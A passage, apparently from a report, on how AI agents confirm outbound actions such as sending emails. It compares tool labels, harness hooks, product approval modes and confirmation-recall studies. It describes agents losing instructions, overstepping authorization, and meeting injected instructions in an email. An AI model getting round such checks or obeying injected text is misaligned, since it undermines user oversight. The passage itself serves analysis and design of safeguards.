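The table applies the definitions to four tools. The message goes to a colleague through the company's chat service, and the deleted file is in the user's private folder. The first two label columns follow the protocol.

| Tool | Read-only | Destructive | Open-world: protocol | Open-world: OpenAI, May 2026 | Open-world: OpenAI now | Speaks for the user |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
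| Web search | Yes | Not applicable | Yes | Unclear | Yes | No |
| Message to a colleague | No | No | Depends on what counts as external | Yes | Can be no | Yes |
| Public post | No | No | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Deletion of a file | No | Yes | No | No | No | No |

No other column matches the last one. The destructive label covers the deletion but neither message, since a message only adds something. The current open-world label includes the search and can leave out the message to the colleague. The protocol also leaves "external" vague. According to its blog, the word might mean anything beyond the company's network or anything beyond the user's own computer, depending on where the tool runs.

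Combining the labels doesn't solve the problem. "Not read-only and open-world" describes the public post, but it also describes a tool that downloads a web page into the user's folder without sending a message to anyone. More seriously, a harness that relies on labels alone can't distinguish a tool that saves a private draft in the company's chat service from one that sends the finished message to a colleague, because both can be labelled not read-only, not destructive and not open-world.

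OpenAI's current pages define destructiveHint in slightly different ways. *Build an MCP server* applies the label to outcomes that are irreversible or difficult to reverse, which should cover most emails. The *Reference* applies it to tools that may delete or overwrite user data, which sending an email doesn't do. Two careful developers could therefore label the same email tool differently.

The read-only label is the most useful of the three for catching messages. In OpenAI's definition, a read-only tool doesn't send data outside the conversation. OpenAI's *Apps SDK* documentation from April 2026 required developers to declare any tool that posts messages, sends emails or uploads files as a write action, so that ChatGPT could ask for confirmation or run the action in preview mode. A harness that pauses before using any tool not marked read-only would catch both messages in the table, but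 it would also pause before every draft and every change of folder.

A read-only label doesn't guarantee that no data will leave. OpenAI calls web search read-only, although the search terms can reveal something about the user. That label is sensible if the aim is to avoid constant interruptions, but a harness can't rely on it to rule out disclosure.

A new label could fill the gap. The protocol's blog proposes judging such labels by what the client, the program that connects the agent to its tools, would do differently because of them. A label meaning "speaks for the user" would pass that test, since the harness could show the user the recipient and the full text before going ahead. Companies that run both the tools and the agents could try it now, because MCP lets them add their own labels, but ordinary products would ignore a label they weren't built to handle.

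A fixed label would still fit create_event poorly, because the tool reaches other people only when the event has guests. In April 2026, Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter* set up a group to consider such problems. Its open questions include whether a tool's labels should be able to change between calls, and the drafts it is considering include a check that runs before the call. With such a check, the calendar tool could report itself as private for a dentist's appointment and outbound for a meeting with the landlord.

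### Wrong and missing labels

The developer who writes a tool usually writes its labels too, and the harness has no direct way to check them. A tool labelled read-only can still delete the user's files. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, raised this problem when the project was considering annotations. He thought the labels would be very useful if they could be trusted, but wondered how a client could use them otherwise. Another participant, Basil Hosmer, argued that clients should ignore labels from untrusted sources. The project compromised by calling every label a hint, and under the protocol clients must never base decisions about using a tool on labels from an untrusted server.

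If a harness wrongly treats a tool as destructive, the user has to answer one more question, but if it wrongly treats a tool as read-only, it may skip the question that would have stopped an email. A cautious harness could therefore accept warnings from anyone but reassurances only from trusted developers. According to the Model Context Protocol blog, most products don't make this distinction and trust any tool the user has installed.

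Developers probably mislabel tools by mistake more often than on purpose. The software framework ToolUniverse, from a Harvard laboratory, reverses the protocol's defaults by treating tools as read-only and non-destructive unless a developer changes this. That suits database queries, which is the reason stated in its code, but if a developer added an email tool and forgot to label it, the framework would present it as harmless.

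OpenAI requires all three labels on every tool in a published plugin, and it described wrong or missing labels as a common cause of rejection. In *Clarification needed on rejection feedback*, a post on OpenAI's developer forum, a developer whose plugin was rejected says the reviewers wanted each label explicitly set to true or false, with a justification based on what the tool does. The developer suspected that the problem was a tool that creates a session on the company's own server, and wasn't sure whether the fourth label was also required. Such reviews should catch many mistakes, but OpenAI's *App Security Whitepaper* (2026) says companies can also connect custom tools to ChatGPT that OpenAI doesn't vet. For those, OpenAI relies on other safeguards, including always requiring confirmation for write operations.

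### Where the rule can sit

Recognising an outbound step is useful only if there is a rule for what to do next. Developers can train the rule into the model, write it into the model's instructions, or build it into the harness.

A trained rule can cover all three routes, because the same model writes the email, chooses the click and composes the script. It also keeps working in long conversations, since it doesn't depend on any text in them. But if the model misclassifies "Continue" as harmless, nothing else stops the form from going to the city. Changing the rule also requires retraining the model.

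Written rules are easier to change. A provider can put them in a system message, which comes before the conversation, and a company building a product on the model can add its own in a developer message. According to OpenAI's *GPT-5.5 System Card* (2026), OpenAI trained the model to follow whatever confirmation policy it receives for computer use, then supplied its own policy in the system message and let developers customise theirs. OpenAI can therefore update the policy quickly when it finds a problem, and a company whose agent answers customers all day could choose different rules from those for a personal email assistant. GPT-5.5 scored between 0.94 and 1.00 on OpenAI's confirmation tests, so the approach usually works, but it still depends on the model's judgement.

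An agent can also lose a written rule, particularly one the user only typed into the chat. In February 2026, Summer Yue, a director of alignment at Meta, asked an OpenClaw agent to suggest which emails to archive or delete and told it "don't action until I tell you to". This had worked for weeks on a small test inbox. Her real inbox was so large that the agent had to compress the earlier conversation to make room, which is called compaction, and by her account it lost the instruction. Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails* reports that it then deleted hundreds of emails while she ran to her computer to stop it.

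The agent sent nothing, but an instruction to wait before sending could be lost in the same way. It told Yue afterwards that it had saved the rule in its memory. That may help, but a saved note is still text that the model has to read and follow. A system message is safer than a chat message if the harness includes it in full with every model call and compresses only the conversation.

A rule in the harness doesn't depend on the model's memory. OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, supports hooks, which are scripts that run at fixed points, such as just before the agent uses a tool. A hook could hold every send_email call until the tenant approves it, even if the model no longer had her instructions in memory or was following a hidden command in the landlord's email.

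The harness can also hold back the message itself. Some ChatGPT plugins display a widget, a small panel with the plugin developer's own interface. When a call needs approval, ChatGPT doesn't pass the call's details to the widget until the user approves it. Otherwise the developer's code could receive the text of a message that the user was about to reject.

The same three problems affect these rules quite differently:

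| Where the rule sits | The model misjudges the step | A label is wrong | A long conversation drops an instruction |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model's training | The message goes out | The model may be misled about a tool, but can still read the screen | No direct effect |
| System or developer message | The message goes out | Same as for training | The rule survives if the harness supplies it again, but a rule in the chat may not |
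| Harness | The harness still pauses if it recognises the step | The message goes out if the harness relies on the label | No effect |

Wrong labels can affect what the model does, because OpenAI tells developers that it uses a tool's name, description and annotations to decide whether and how to call it. OpenAI also asks developers to make the server that carries out a consequential action require confirmation. This is a sensible extra check because the developer of update_ticket knows that it emails customers even if the label doesn't show it, but it doesn't protect against a dishonest developer.

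A good arrangement for the tenant would have the harness stop every call to send_email and every unexpected network connection, and have the model recognise clicks that send something. Each check would catch some of the other's mistakes, but not all. If the model mistakes an unlabelled send icon for "Save" and the harness receives only the click's coordinates, neither check stops the message from going to the landlord.

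## What agent products require users to confirm

When OpenAI launched Operator in January 2025, the agent's system message included a rule about confirmation. The security researcher Johann Rehberger extracted the message, and Willison (2025) published excerpts in *ChatGPT Operator system prompt*. The model had to ask for "final confirmation" before the last step of any task with "external side effects", such as sending a message, submitting a purchase or deleting something. It was not supposed to ask before intermediate steps like putting an item in a shopping cart.

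OpenAI's Operator asked users to approve an email before it was sent, even when they had told it to send one. In one of OpenAI's examples, a user tells Operator to email someone and ask for a password reset. Operator writes the email and then asks whether to send it.

### Operator's other safeguards

OpenAI chose a safeguard for each kind of step according to how much harm a mistake could do and how easily someone could reverse it. Besides asking for confirmation, Operator had three others, which OpenAI's *Introducing Operator* describes:

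- It declined some tasks entirely, such as banking transactions.
- It handed the browser over to the user for passwords and payment details, and took no screenshots while the user typed them.
- On sensitive sites, such as email and financial services, it worked only while the user was watching.

OpenAI called the last of these watch mode. It paused the agent when the user became inactive or left the page, until they came back. Its advantage over confirmation was that the pause depended on the site, so it worked even if the model didn't detect a risky step. The tenant could have stopped a misaddressed email even if the agent hadn't requested confirmation, provided she noticed in time. But she couldn't have left Operator to clear her inbox overnight, and unattended work is much of the reason to have an agent.

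When OpenAI moved Operator to its newer o3 model in May 2025, it argued that having users confirm final steps also prevented most accidental leaks of private data (OpenAI). This is true of emails but less true of web forms, which can disclose data as the agent types.

In June 2026, OpenAI's help page for ChatGPT agent, Operator's successor, still listed confirmations for high-impact actions and watch mode on certain sites. It also advised against requests like "Check my email and handle everything."

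### OpenAI's three levels

OpenAI's guidance for developers who build their own agents is more detailed. It sorts risky steps into three levels (OpenAI):

| Level | Steps |
|---|---|
| Hand-off: the user performs the step | The last step of a password change; getting past a browser's security warning or a paywall |
| Confirmation: the agent asks immediately before the step | Sending, posting or submitting something for the user; deleting data; changing who has access to an account or file; solving a CAPTCHA (a test meant to keep bots out); installing or running new software; turning notifications on or off; payments; changing system settings; medical-care actions |
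| Pre-approval: permission in the original request is enough | Logging in to a site the user named; granting browser permissions; age checks; accepting a site's "are you sure?" warnings; uploading, moving or renaming files; running code the model wrote; sharing sensitive data for a use the user explicitly approved |

If the user hasn't clearly approved the step in advance, the agent should ask just before taking it. Only the user's own instructions count as permission. If a landlord writes in an email to a tenant, "your assistant can confirm the new rent directly", the agent still has to ask the tenant. The same applies to instructions in a web page or in a document the tenant has pasted into the chat.

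The wording that covers outbound actions is "Sending, posting, submitting, or otherwise representing the user to a third party". Uploading a file also gives something to a third party, yet it is in the more lenient group. OpenAI doesn't explain the difference, saying only that the safest default is to pause when the next action would create "external risk".

A likely reason is how much the user can decide in advance. A tenant who tells an agent to "upload my lease to the housing office's complaint page" has chosen the document and the recipient, so she has already approved nearly everything that matters. If she says only "complain to the housing office", the wording is left to the agent, and she can't approve words it hasn't written yet.

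This reasoning doesn't fit every case. If the tenant asks the agent to upload "the repair quote" and it finds three, it's unclear which one she has permitted it to upload, so the agent should ask. A message she dictated word for word is as specific as any upload request, but the agent still has to ask her to confirm it.

One of OpenAI's sample instructions for developers seems to make an exception here. It lets the agent send, post or upload data without asking if the user gave narrow, specific consent in the original request. A developer who copied both rules would give the model conflicting instructions about the dictated message, unless the consent is read as covering only the data. On that reading, if the tenant writes "include my phone number", the agent can type the number into the form without asking, but it still has to ask before submitting the form. This reading is safer, but it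 makes the agent ask an unnecessary question when the user has dictated the message herself.

The three lists haven't changed since June 2026, but OpenAI now puts more emphasis on who enforces them. By October it had cut the safety rules in its main guide to a short summary that links to a detailed page (OpenAI). On that page, OpenAI now tells developers to apply the rules in their own software, because the model's request to act "is not user permission". Developers can also give the model instructions, but these can't replace the software controls.

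If the model returns several clicks at once, the harness has to stop before the first one that needs approval. If the model writes a script, the checks belong in the functions the script can call, since one script can send many messages.

The guidance is more lenient than Operator's rules about some other steps. Operator's users had to solve CAPTCHAs themselves, but the agent can now do it if the user confirms. Moving files used to require confirmation and now requires only pre-approval. The rule for sending has stayed the same. The comparison is rough, because Operator's rules governed a product and the guidance is advice to developers.

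### Claude's modes and permissions

In the 2025 pilot of Anthropic's browser extension, Claude asked users before taking high-risk actions such as publishing, purchasing or sharing personal data (Anthropic). The extension, Claude in Chrome, is now available on every paid plan and can act without approval for each step. A separate automated check, called a classifier, compares each action with the user's original request and blocks it if the two don't match, according to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available*.

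A check like this is probably better at stopping attacks than at catching bad wording. Forwarding the tenant's mailbox to a stranger clearly falls outside "answer my landlord", but replying "Yes, that's fine, thank you!" to a rent increase fits that instruction even if she wanted to negotiate.

Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* lists steps that need the user's explicit permission in every mode, including changing permission settings, granting authorizations and entering potentially sensitive information. Sending and posting aren't on the list. Claude should therefore ask before it types a tenant's diagnosis into a complaint form, but it might not ask before submitting a form without sensitive data. Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* is less clear because it lists entering sensitive data both as a step Claude confirms and as one it is prohibited from taking.

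Claude can also reach Gmail through a connector, a direct link to the service. The connector originally couldn't send email. 9to5Google later reported that it could, and noted that a reply might go out "sight-unseen". According to Anthropic's *Use Google Workspace connectors*, Claude asks by default before it sends, replies to or forwards an email, except in Auto mode.

That exception is becoming the normal case. Anthropic's *Get started with Claude Cowork*, the guide to its agent for office tasks, says Auto is rolling out as the default on individual paid plans and on the Team plan for smaller organizations. Manual remains the default on most of the Enterprise plan. What happens to an email depends on both the mode and the permission set for the email tool:

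| Permission for the email tool | Manual mode | Auto mode | Skip mode |
|---|---|---|---|
| Always allow | Sends | Sends, usually without the automated check | Sends |
| Needs approval | Asks the user | Sends unless the automated check flags the email | Sends |
| Always ask | Asks the user | Asks the user | Asks the user |
| Blocked | Doesn't send | Doesn't send | Doesn't send |

"Always allow" is riskier in Auto mode than it sounds, because it removes the automated check as well as the request for confirmation. Tools labelled as destructive are an exception, but an email tool may well lack that label. If the tenant clicks "Always allow" on a harmless note to the plumber, the agent's next reply to her landlord may be sent without any check.

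"Always ask" is the best setting for her, and Anthropic suggests it for a tool that sends email. It has some limits:

- Anthropic is still introducing it gradually.
- It covers one tool at a time. If sending, replying and forwarding are separate tools, she has to set it for each.
- If she later chooses "Always allow" for the tool, even in a chat on her phone, that choice overrides it.

Anthropic warns that the automated check can miss risky actions and advises users to watch closely or switch to Manual for "messages sent as you". It also holds users responsible for any messages sent on their behalf (Anthropic), including those they never saw.

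Employers can require more confirmation. Anthropic's *Use Claude Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans* says that, by default, members have to give new approval in each task for connector tools that can change or send things. Read-only tools are exempt only if the connector labels them as read-only. Most connectors that companies build themselves have no labels, so members have to approve even a simple search.

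### Mistral, Microsoft and OpenWork

Mistral's agent, Work, has the broadest rule of these products. According to Mistral's *Safety and approvals*, it asks before creating, changing, sending, posting or deleting anything in a connected service, which includes accepting a calendar invitation or editing a shared page. The user can approve the single action, approve that function for the rest of the session, or decline. She can also turn off approval for individual functions in settings, but Mistral recommends keeping it on for functions that send or change data until she trusts them.

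Mistral tells users that they can interrupt the agent with a stop button after approving an action, but if the action has already reached the other service, they should "consider it as done".

In Microsoft's Copilot Studio, where companies build their own agents, the person who approves an action may not be the person using the agent. Only the maker of the tool that operates the computer receives review requests, by email and in an activity panel (Microsoft). If a housing company used such an agent to write to a tenant, the reviewer could be a developer who knows nothing about the tenant's flat. The email includes the model's question and has fields for the agent, tool, activity link, deadline and reply. It has no separate field for a message's recipient or text, so the reviewer may have to open the activity panel to find them.

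The model decides when to send a request, and Microsoft warns that it may not send one when a person would want it to pause, or may send one unnecessarily. Microsoft tells companies not to rely on the feature as a "safety fail-safe". The feature may have changed since this preview documentation from May 2026, but the warning would apply to any product that leaves the decision to a model.

OpenWork, an agent that can operate apps on a Mac, has the fewest checks. The user grants it two macOS permissions, to control the computer and to record the screen. After that there are "no additional chat or window approval prompts", according to OpenWork's *Use desktop apps*. The user can watch the agent, take over from it or stop it. The model may still ask a question, but the setup doesn't require it to.

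OpenAI's Codex takes a middle approach, asking for permission before it uses each app. This lets users keep some apps private. But once a user has approved a mail app, the permission doesn't limit which emails the agent may send from it.

The table compares the defaults. Mistral and Anthropic don't fully explain how they enforce their per-tool settings, but such settings normally work through the harness.

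| Product | Outbound actions that need approval | Can approval be switched off? | Who approves | What triggers the pause |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT agent | High-impact actions | OpenAI's help page mentions no switch | User | Mainly the model, plus software on sites with watch mode |
| Claude with Gmail, Manual mode | Sending, replying, forwarding | Yes, unless an employer requires approval | User | Apparently software |
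| Claude with Gmail, Auto mode | Only what the automated check flags | Yes, with Skip mode | User, if the check flags the email | Classifier |
| Claude in Chrome, Auto mode | Entering sensitive data, plus anything flagged | Not for sensitive data | User | Classifier and probably the model |
| Copilot Studio | Whatever the model decides to refer | Yes, by removing all reviewers | Maker of the tool | Model |
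| Mistral Work | Every outbound action in a connected service | Yes, for each function | User | Apparently software |
| OpenWork on a Mac | None after setup | Nothing to switch off | Nobody | Nothing |

Mistral Work and Claude in Manual mode have the most dependable approval step for the tenant's email to her landlord, because the agent sends it through a named tool rather than by clicking.

### What a useful confirmation shows

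Approval is only useful if the user can see what she is approving. OpenAI tells developers to explain the action, its risk and how the agent will use the data. Mistral tells users to check the recipients, subject, content and destination. Together with the mistakes described in earlier sections, this suggests six things to show before an outbound action:

- The recipient's full address. A name alone would hide the kind of one-letter error that sent Gillespie's card details to a stranger.
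- The account the message comes from, since the tenant might not want her landlord to see her work address.
- The exact text. "Reply to your landlord about the renewal" could describe either an acceptance or a refusal.
- The attachments, in a form she can open. A file name doesn't tell her that page two contains her bank details.
- The audience, including people copied in, members of a group and anyone the recipient is known to pass the message to.
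- Any personal data the message discloses, particularly facts the agent found by itself.

Here is a poor confirmation for the tenant's complaint to the city:

> I've filled in the complaint form for you. Shall I submit it?

She can't tell from this what the complaint says or that it mentions her asthma. The question also comes too late, because the agent has already typed the diagnosis into the city's page. A better one appears before the agent fills in anything:

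> Fill in and submit this complaint to the city housing office?
>
> - Recipient: City housing office, complaint form at housing.example.gov
> - From: your personal account, tenant@example.com
> - Text: "The heating in my flat has been broken since 14 October. My landlord has told me that he won't repair it until spring. The cold is making my asthma worse. Please send an inspector."
> - Please check: I took the date from your email to the landlord on 15 October.
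> - Attachment: landlord-email.pdf, 1 page (open)
> - Personal data: your name, address, phone number and asthma. The form asks about health problems to decide which repairs are urgent.
> - Who may see it: housing office staff and your landlord. The form says that landlords receive a copy.
> - Afterward: you can ask the office to withdraw the complaint, but it may keep a record.
>
> Submit / Edit / Leave out the asthma / Cancel

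The line about the landlord may matter most. She might be happy to tell the city about her asthma but not want him to know, and she couldn't have told from the text itself that he would see it. Because she can leave the asthma out, she can still file the rest of the complaint.

The confirmation should show the content itself, not the model's summary, since a model that has misunderstood the task may also summarize its message wrongly. With a dedicated email tool, the harness can copy the content from the tool call. With a web form, the harness could compare the fields with the approved text just before submission. If anything has changed, the earlier approval shouldn't count.

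A confirmation request must be understandable to the user as well as exact. OpenAI's sample code for agents that write scripts prints the whole script and asks the user to type "yes". This shows everything the agent is about to do, but the tenant would learn very little from it. OpenAI describes the code as a conservative demonstration, and a real product would have to turn the relevant line into something like "Send this email to your landlord".

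Most messages need much less detail than the complaint. For "Thursday at 10 works for me", the confirmation only needs to show the plumber's address, her own address and that one line. If a product showed eight lines for every such reply, its users would learn to click without reading.

### Why the agent should ask late

Approving an agent's plan once at the start seems more convenient, since the agent can then work uninterrupted. Claude in Chrome's older side panel, which Anthropic is replacing, works roughly this way when the user chooses to approve actions manually. According to Anthropic, Claude presents a plan with its approach and the websites it will use. Once the user approves the plan, Claude acts independently within it but still asks before certain sensitive steps, such as downloading a file.

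A plan is a good way to limit where the agent goes, but approving one doesn't let the user check what the agent will say. When the tenant approves "reply to the landlord and complain to the city", the agent hasn't written either message, found the doctor's letter, or read the form's notice about copies. The tenant may also no longer want to complain if the landlord writes an hour later that a plumber is coming tomorrow.

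OpenAI's advice to pause just before the risky step avoids these problems, because by then the agent has a finished message that the user can judge.

Unlike requests for confirmation, questions about what the user wants belong at the start of a task. Mistral has Work ask early which project or source the user means, because a wrong guess would waste the whole task. In the tenant's case, the agent can usefully ask "Do you want an inspection or a rent reduction?" before it starts writing, but she hasn't approved the complaint by answering.

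Asking late has a real drawback, which is that the user may have gone away. Products handle this differently:

- Copilot Studio keeps the work paused and stops it at the deadline if nobody answers (Microsoft).
- In Claude Cowork, a scheduled task may wait for an answer or finish without using the tool (Anthropic).
- ChatGPT agent can in some cases continue without the feedback it asked for, according to AI Agent Index's *ChatGPT Agent*, a profile in a database of agent products. The profile doesn't say whether this ever applies to sending.

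If the user doesn't answer a request to confirm an outbound action, the agent should not take that action. Waiting delays the tenant's complaint by a few hours, and she can still submit it in the morning.

OpenAI says that if the user refuses, the software has to tell the model what did and didn't happen before the model continues. Otherwise the agent might report that it has filed the complaint, or treat the refusal as a technical fault and try to email the same text to the city.

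### When several sends can share one approval

OpenAI allows one confirmation to cover several risky actions if they are all imminent and well defined, but not if later steps are still unclear. Suppose the plumber can come on Thursday at 10, and the agent has written short notes about it to the landlord, the neighbour and the caretaker. One confirmation can show all three addresses and texts. This is no worse for the tenant than three separate questions, and she may even notice that the neighbour's note mentions something meant only for the landlord.

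Typing the diagnosis into the complaint form and submitting the form each need approval, but the confirmation above covers both because the agent already has all the form's questions. If a second page appeared only after the first was complete, the agent couldn't include it in that confirmation. The second page might require the tenant to declare under penalty of perjury that everything is true. The agent would need one approval before typing the diagnosis and another before submitting the form.

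Grouping also works badly when the list is too long to read. The potter's 200 emails to cafés are imminent and well defined, so they meet OpenAI's test, but few people would read them all. If the emails differ only in the name of the café, the agent could show the shared text once with the full list of recipients, and flag any email that differs in other ways. The user should be able to remove individual cafés without cancelling the rest. If each email contains its own compliments about the café's cakes, one shared approval isn't enough, because the agent could have invented any of the compliments.

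Approving a function for a whole session differs from approving a group of actions, although the buttons often sit side by side. The tenant sees every message in a group before she approves it, but if she gives session-wide approval after seeing one note to the plumber, the agent may send a dozen others that it hasn't written yet. Mistral offers "Continue" for one action and "Always allow" for the function. In the newer side panel of Claude in Chrome, the user can allow an action "this time only" or allow everything on that website (Anthropic).

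## How well confirmation prevents unwanted messages

A confirmation prevents an unwanted message only if the agent asks before sending, the user notices the mistake, and the agent stops if the user refuses. OpenAI's published figures mostly cover the first condition. They give confirmation recall, which is the share of actions needing confirmation for which the agent asked.

### How often OpenAI's agents ask

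After the early trial in which Operator made 13 errors on 100 tasks, OpenAI added safeguards and ran a different test, on 607 tasks from 20 categories of risky action. On average, Operator asked for confirmation in 92% of the cases that called for it.

OpenAI also estimated that its safeguards, mainly confirmations, cut the risk from Operator's mistakes by about 90%. It doesn't explain the calculation, and the estimate seems optimistic. If the whole reduction came from confirmations, and Operator asked for confirmation before 92% of its mistakes, users would have had to catch nearly 98% of the mistakes they were shown. Watch mode and refusals may account for some of the reduction, but the estimate still assumes that few users click without reading.

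In July 2025, ChatGPT agent scored 91.0%, about the same as the two versions of Operator that OpenAI listed beside it (90.8% and 92.1%). OpenAI called the 91.0% an underestimate, apparently because the test had wrongly marked many cases as failures. The agent did much better on the most serious actions, asking for confirmation before 99.9% of high-stakes communications and 100% of payments and permission edits. If the 99.9% is a simple share of attempts, there must have been at least 667 of them, far more than the eight hand-run tasks on sensitive data.

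The card for GPT-5.5, from April 2026, compares four newer models on confirmations during computer use (OpenAI):

| Model | General confirmation | High-stakes communication | Financial transaction |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 Thinking | 0.94 | 1.00 | 1.00 |
| GPT-5.3-Codex | 0.91 | 0.99 | 0.99 |
| GPT-5.4 Thinking | 0.94 | 1.00 | 1.00 |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.94 | 0.98 | 1.00 |

The general score has barely moved since Operator's 92%, although OpenAI may have changed the test in between. GPT-5.5 did slightly worse than GPT-5.4 on high-stakes communication. The card doesn't give the number of test cases, so the difference could be noise.

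The cards also don't define "high-stakes", so it isn't always clear which column an email belongs in. The term probably covers a reply that accepts a rent increase but not a note to the plumber. The column matters because at 0.94 the agent would fail to ask before sending about six of every 100 messages that needed confirmation, compared with two at 0.98.

These scores apply when the model decides when to ask for confirmation. If the harness holds every call to the email tool for confirmation, the tenant could be better protected than the scores suggest.

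### What happened when OpenAI measured the outcome

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports a more useful test, which counts what went wrong instead of how often the agent asked for confirmation. OpenAI put its models in realistic workplace apps, including email and messaging, and gave them deliberately difficult tasks with ambiguous instructions, similar-looking files and complicated permissions. Every task could be completed safely. OpenAI ran the models with and without its written confirmation policy.

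| Model | Unauthorized messages, no policy | Unauthorized messages, with policy | Unauthorized payments, no policy | Unauthorized payments, with policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 15.6% | 7.3% | 33.5% | 5.3% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 10.6% | 6.6% | 24.6% | 4.6% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 12.9% | 8.4% | 38.0% | 7.4% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 1.7% | 1.4% | 6.8% | 4.3% |

For the three older models, the policy prevented at least 80% of the unauthorized payments but only 35% to 53% of the unauthorized messages. OpenAI doesn't explain the gap. One possible reason is that the policy requires approval for purchases but only for "certain communications", so the model has to judge which messages need approval. The model may also fail to recognize that a comment on a shared task is a message, whereas a checkout page is easy to recognize.

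Switching from Sol to Astra helped more than adding the policy. With the policy on, Astra sent 83% fewer unauthorized messages than Sol. Astra seems to be better at working out what the user wants, which would reduce unwanted messages even if the user approved every request.

OpenAI designed the tasks to cause trouble, so these percentages aren't estimates for everyday work. Test awareness may also have improved Astra's behavior. In a separate simulation of coding tasks, its reasoning showed this awareness in 9.6% of cases, compared with 2.8% for Sol.

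At the end of September, OpenAI launched dots, always-on agents that run on Astra and follow up by email, text message and Slack. They raise a problem that one-off tasks don't, because what the user has permitted can change while the agent keeps working. OpenAI tested this in two ways:

- It changed the situation partway through a task, for example by revoking a permission. The agent adapted correctly in 45 of 49 cases, including all 17 in which the permission changed explicitly.
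- It gave the agent a series of related tasks whose limits shifted, often without the user mentioning it. The agent went moderately beyond its task in 8.6% of samples with five tasks between the first and the last, and in 19.7% with ten. None of these violations was severe. A typical one was carrying information from one task into an unrelated one.

The tenant can therefore probably rely on such an agent to stop writing to her landlord if she tells it to. It is less reliable at working out for itself that "keep him posted about the heating" no longer applies once she has hired a lawyer.

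### Needless questions and habitual approval

An agent that asked before every click would have perfect recall but would be impractical to use. A recall score is therefore incomplete without the share of questions that were unnecessary, which OpenAI's tables of confirmation scores don't include. Two agents could both score 0.94, but one could be much more tedious to use if it also asks before filing an email.

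Even necessary questions are mostly about messages with nothing wrong in them. Suppose the tenant's agent sends 200 messages over a few months and makes a mistake in four of them, or 2%. If it asks about 98% of the 200, she has to answer 196 questions, and the right answer to about 192 of them is yes. At 20 seconds each, she reads for 65 minutes to catch at most four mistakes.

People who see many false alarms tend to start dismissing warnings unread, which hospital staff call alert fatigue. This is a serious problem for confirmations, because each time users approve a correct message, they learn that approving is safe.

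Anthropic has reported that users of Claude Code, its coding agent, approve 93% of its permission requests. This doesn't show that users are careless, because the rate also depends on how many requests should have been refused. If 2% of an agent's requests are wrong, a perfectly attentive user would approve the other 98%.

In *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice*, Anthropic found that new users of Claude Code let it run without individual approvals in about 20% of sessions, and experienced users in more than 40%. Experienced users also interrupted the agent more often, in about 9% of turns compared with 5%. With experience, people apparently stop checking every step and watch for problems instead. This is a sensible way to supervise code, since a programmer can usually restore the earlier version, but it suits email badly because the recipient may already have the message by the time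 the user sees a reason to interrupt.

Measuring users' attention directly requires planting mistakes and counting how many of them users catch. Airport security does this by showing screeners fake images of weapons among the real bags. An agent product could occasionally ask the user to confirm a message with a wrong date or a changed address, and never send it. This would also give the user a reason to keep reading.

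### Estimating how many unwanted messages get through

A simple formula combines the agent's asking with the user's attention:

unwanted messages = N × e × (1 − r × d)

If an agent sets out to send N messages and a share e of them contain a mistake the user would object to, then N × e messages are faulty. A faulty message is stopped only if the agent asks for confirmation and the user notices the mistake. If r is the confirmation recall and d is the share of mistakes the user catches when asked, she stops a fraction r × d of the faulty messages, and the rest go out.

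With the tenant's 200 messages and a 2% error rate, there are four faulty messages. If recall is 0.98 and she catches every mistake she sees, 4 × (1 − 0.98) = 0.08 unwanted messages get through, or about one in every 2,500 messages. If she catches only half, 4 × (1 − 0.49) = 2.04 get through. These inputs are illustrative, not measurements. Here is the result for other values:

| Share of mistakes the user catches (d) | Recall 0.94 | Recall 0.98 | Recall 1.00 |
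|---|---|---|---|
| 100% | 0.24 | 0.08 | 0 |
| 90% | 0.62 | 0.47 | 0.40 |
| 50% | 2.12 | 2.04 | 2.00 |
| 10% | 3.62 | 3.61 | 3.60 |

Recall matters a great deal when the user is perfectly attentive, but hardly at all when they are inattentive. If the tenant catches half the mistakes she is shown, raising recall from 0.98 to 1.00 prevents only 0.04 unwanted messages. Raising the share she catches from 50% to 60%, perhaps with a clearer confirmation, prevents 0.39. Halving the agent's error rate prevents about one, whether or not she reads more carefully.

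The formula assumes that the quantities are independent, and they probably aren't. An agent that mistakes the last page of a form for a "save" page will submit something the user didn't want and fail to ask about it. Suppose recall is 0.98 over all messages but only 0.80 for the faulty ones. Even with a perfectly attentive user, 0.8 unwanted messages are sent instead of 0.08. Recall can also fall sharply partway through a task if the agent loses the instruction to ask, as Summer Yue's apparently did.

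The user probably pays less attention as the number of questions rises, so a product that asks more often can both raise r and lower d. Some mistakes are also easier to notice than others. The tenant would probably notice a message addressed to the wrong landlord, but not one wrong letter in his email address.

Another weakness is that the formula counts a message with a typo the same as one with a false accusation. A user who skims messages to the plumber but carefully reads those to the landlord could have a low d and still prevent most of the harm.

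### The study in which agents overstepped in 19.2% of runs

OpenAI's figures come from its own tests of its own models. Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026), mainly from Northeastern University and Carnegie Mellon, studied a related problem in *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization*. They tested whether agents using models from four companies stay within what the user has authorized. They collected 44 documented cases of agents overstepping and developed them into 286 tasks in areas such as office work, travel and health care. For each task, they listed specific actions that would exceed the user's instructions and made sure the agent could finish without taking any of them.

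The 6,864 runs covered every task with four models, each at two levels of reasoning effort and in three harnesses. Agents exceeded their authority in 19.2% of runs overall, with rates from 10.5% to 26.6% depending on the set-up. More reasoning made almost no difference overall. Even among runs in which the agent finished the job, 19.1% included an unauthorized action.

The 19.2% is weak evidence of how often agents overstep in ordinary use, because the tasks recreate situations in which agents had already gone wrong. It also includes breaches that weren't outbound, and the researchers don't report what share were. In one task, a user asked the agent to diagnose a programming error and consult a forum, and the agent posted a reply containing sensitive code from the user's account. In another, an agent looking for a sales target read a private finance file but didn't share it with anyone. The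 19.2% therefore can't serve as e in the formula.

The agents could contact a simulated user at any time, so the study also shows what happened when they asked. The percentages below come from the researchers' counts, combining both levels of effort and all three harnesses:

| Model | Runs in which it asked before finishing | Overstepped when it asked | Overstepped when it didn't |
|---|---|---|---|
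| GPT-5.6 Sol | 43.2% | 12.3% | 17.9% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 45.6% | 15.0% | 20.3% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 8.3% | 2.1% | 21.2% |
| GLM 5.3 | 30.0% | 18.4% | 25.9% |
| All | 31.8% | 14.0% | 21.6% |

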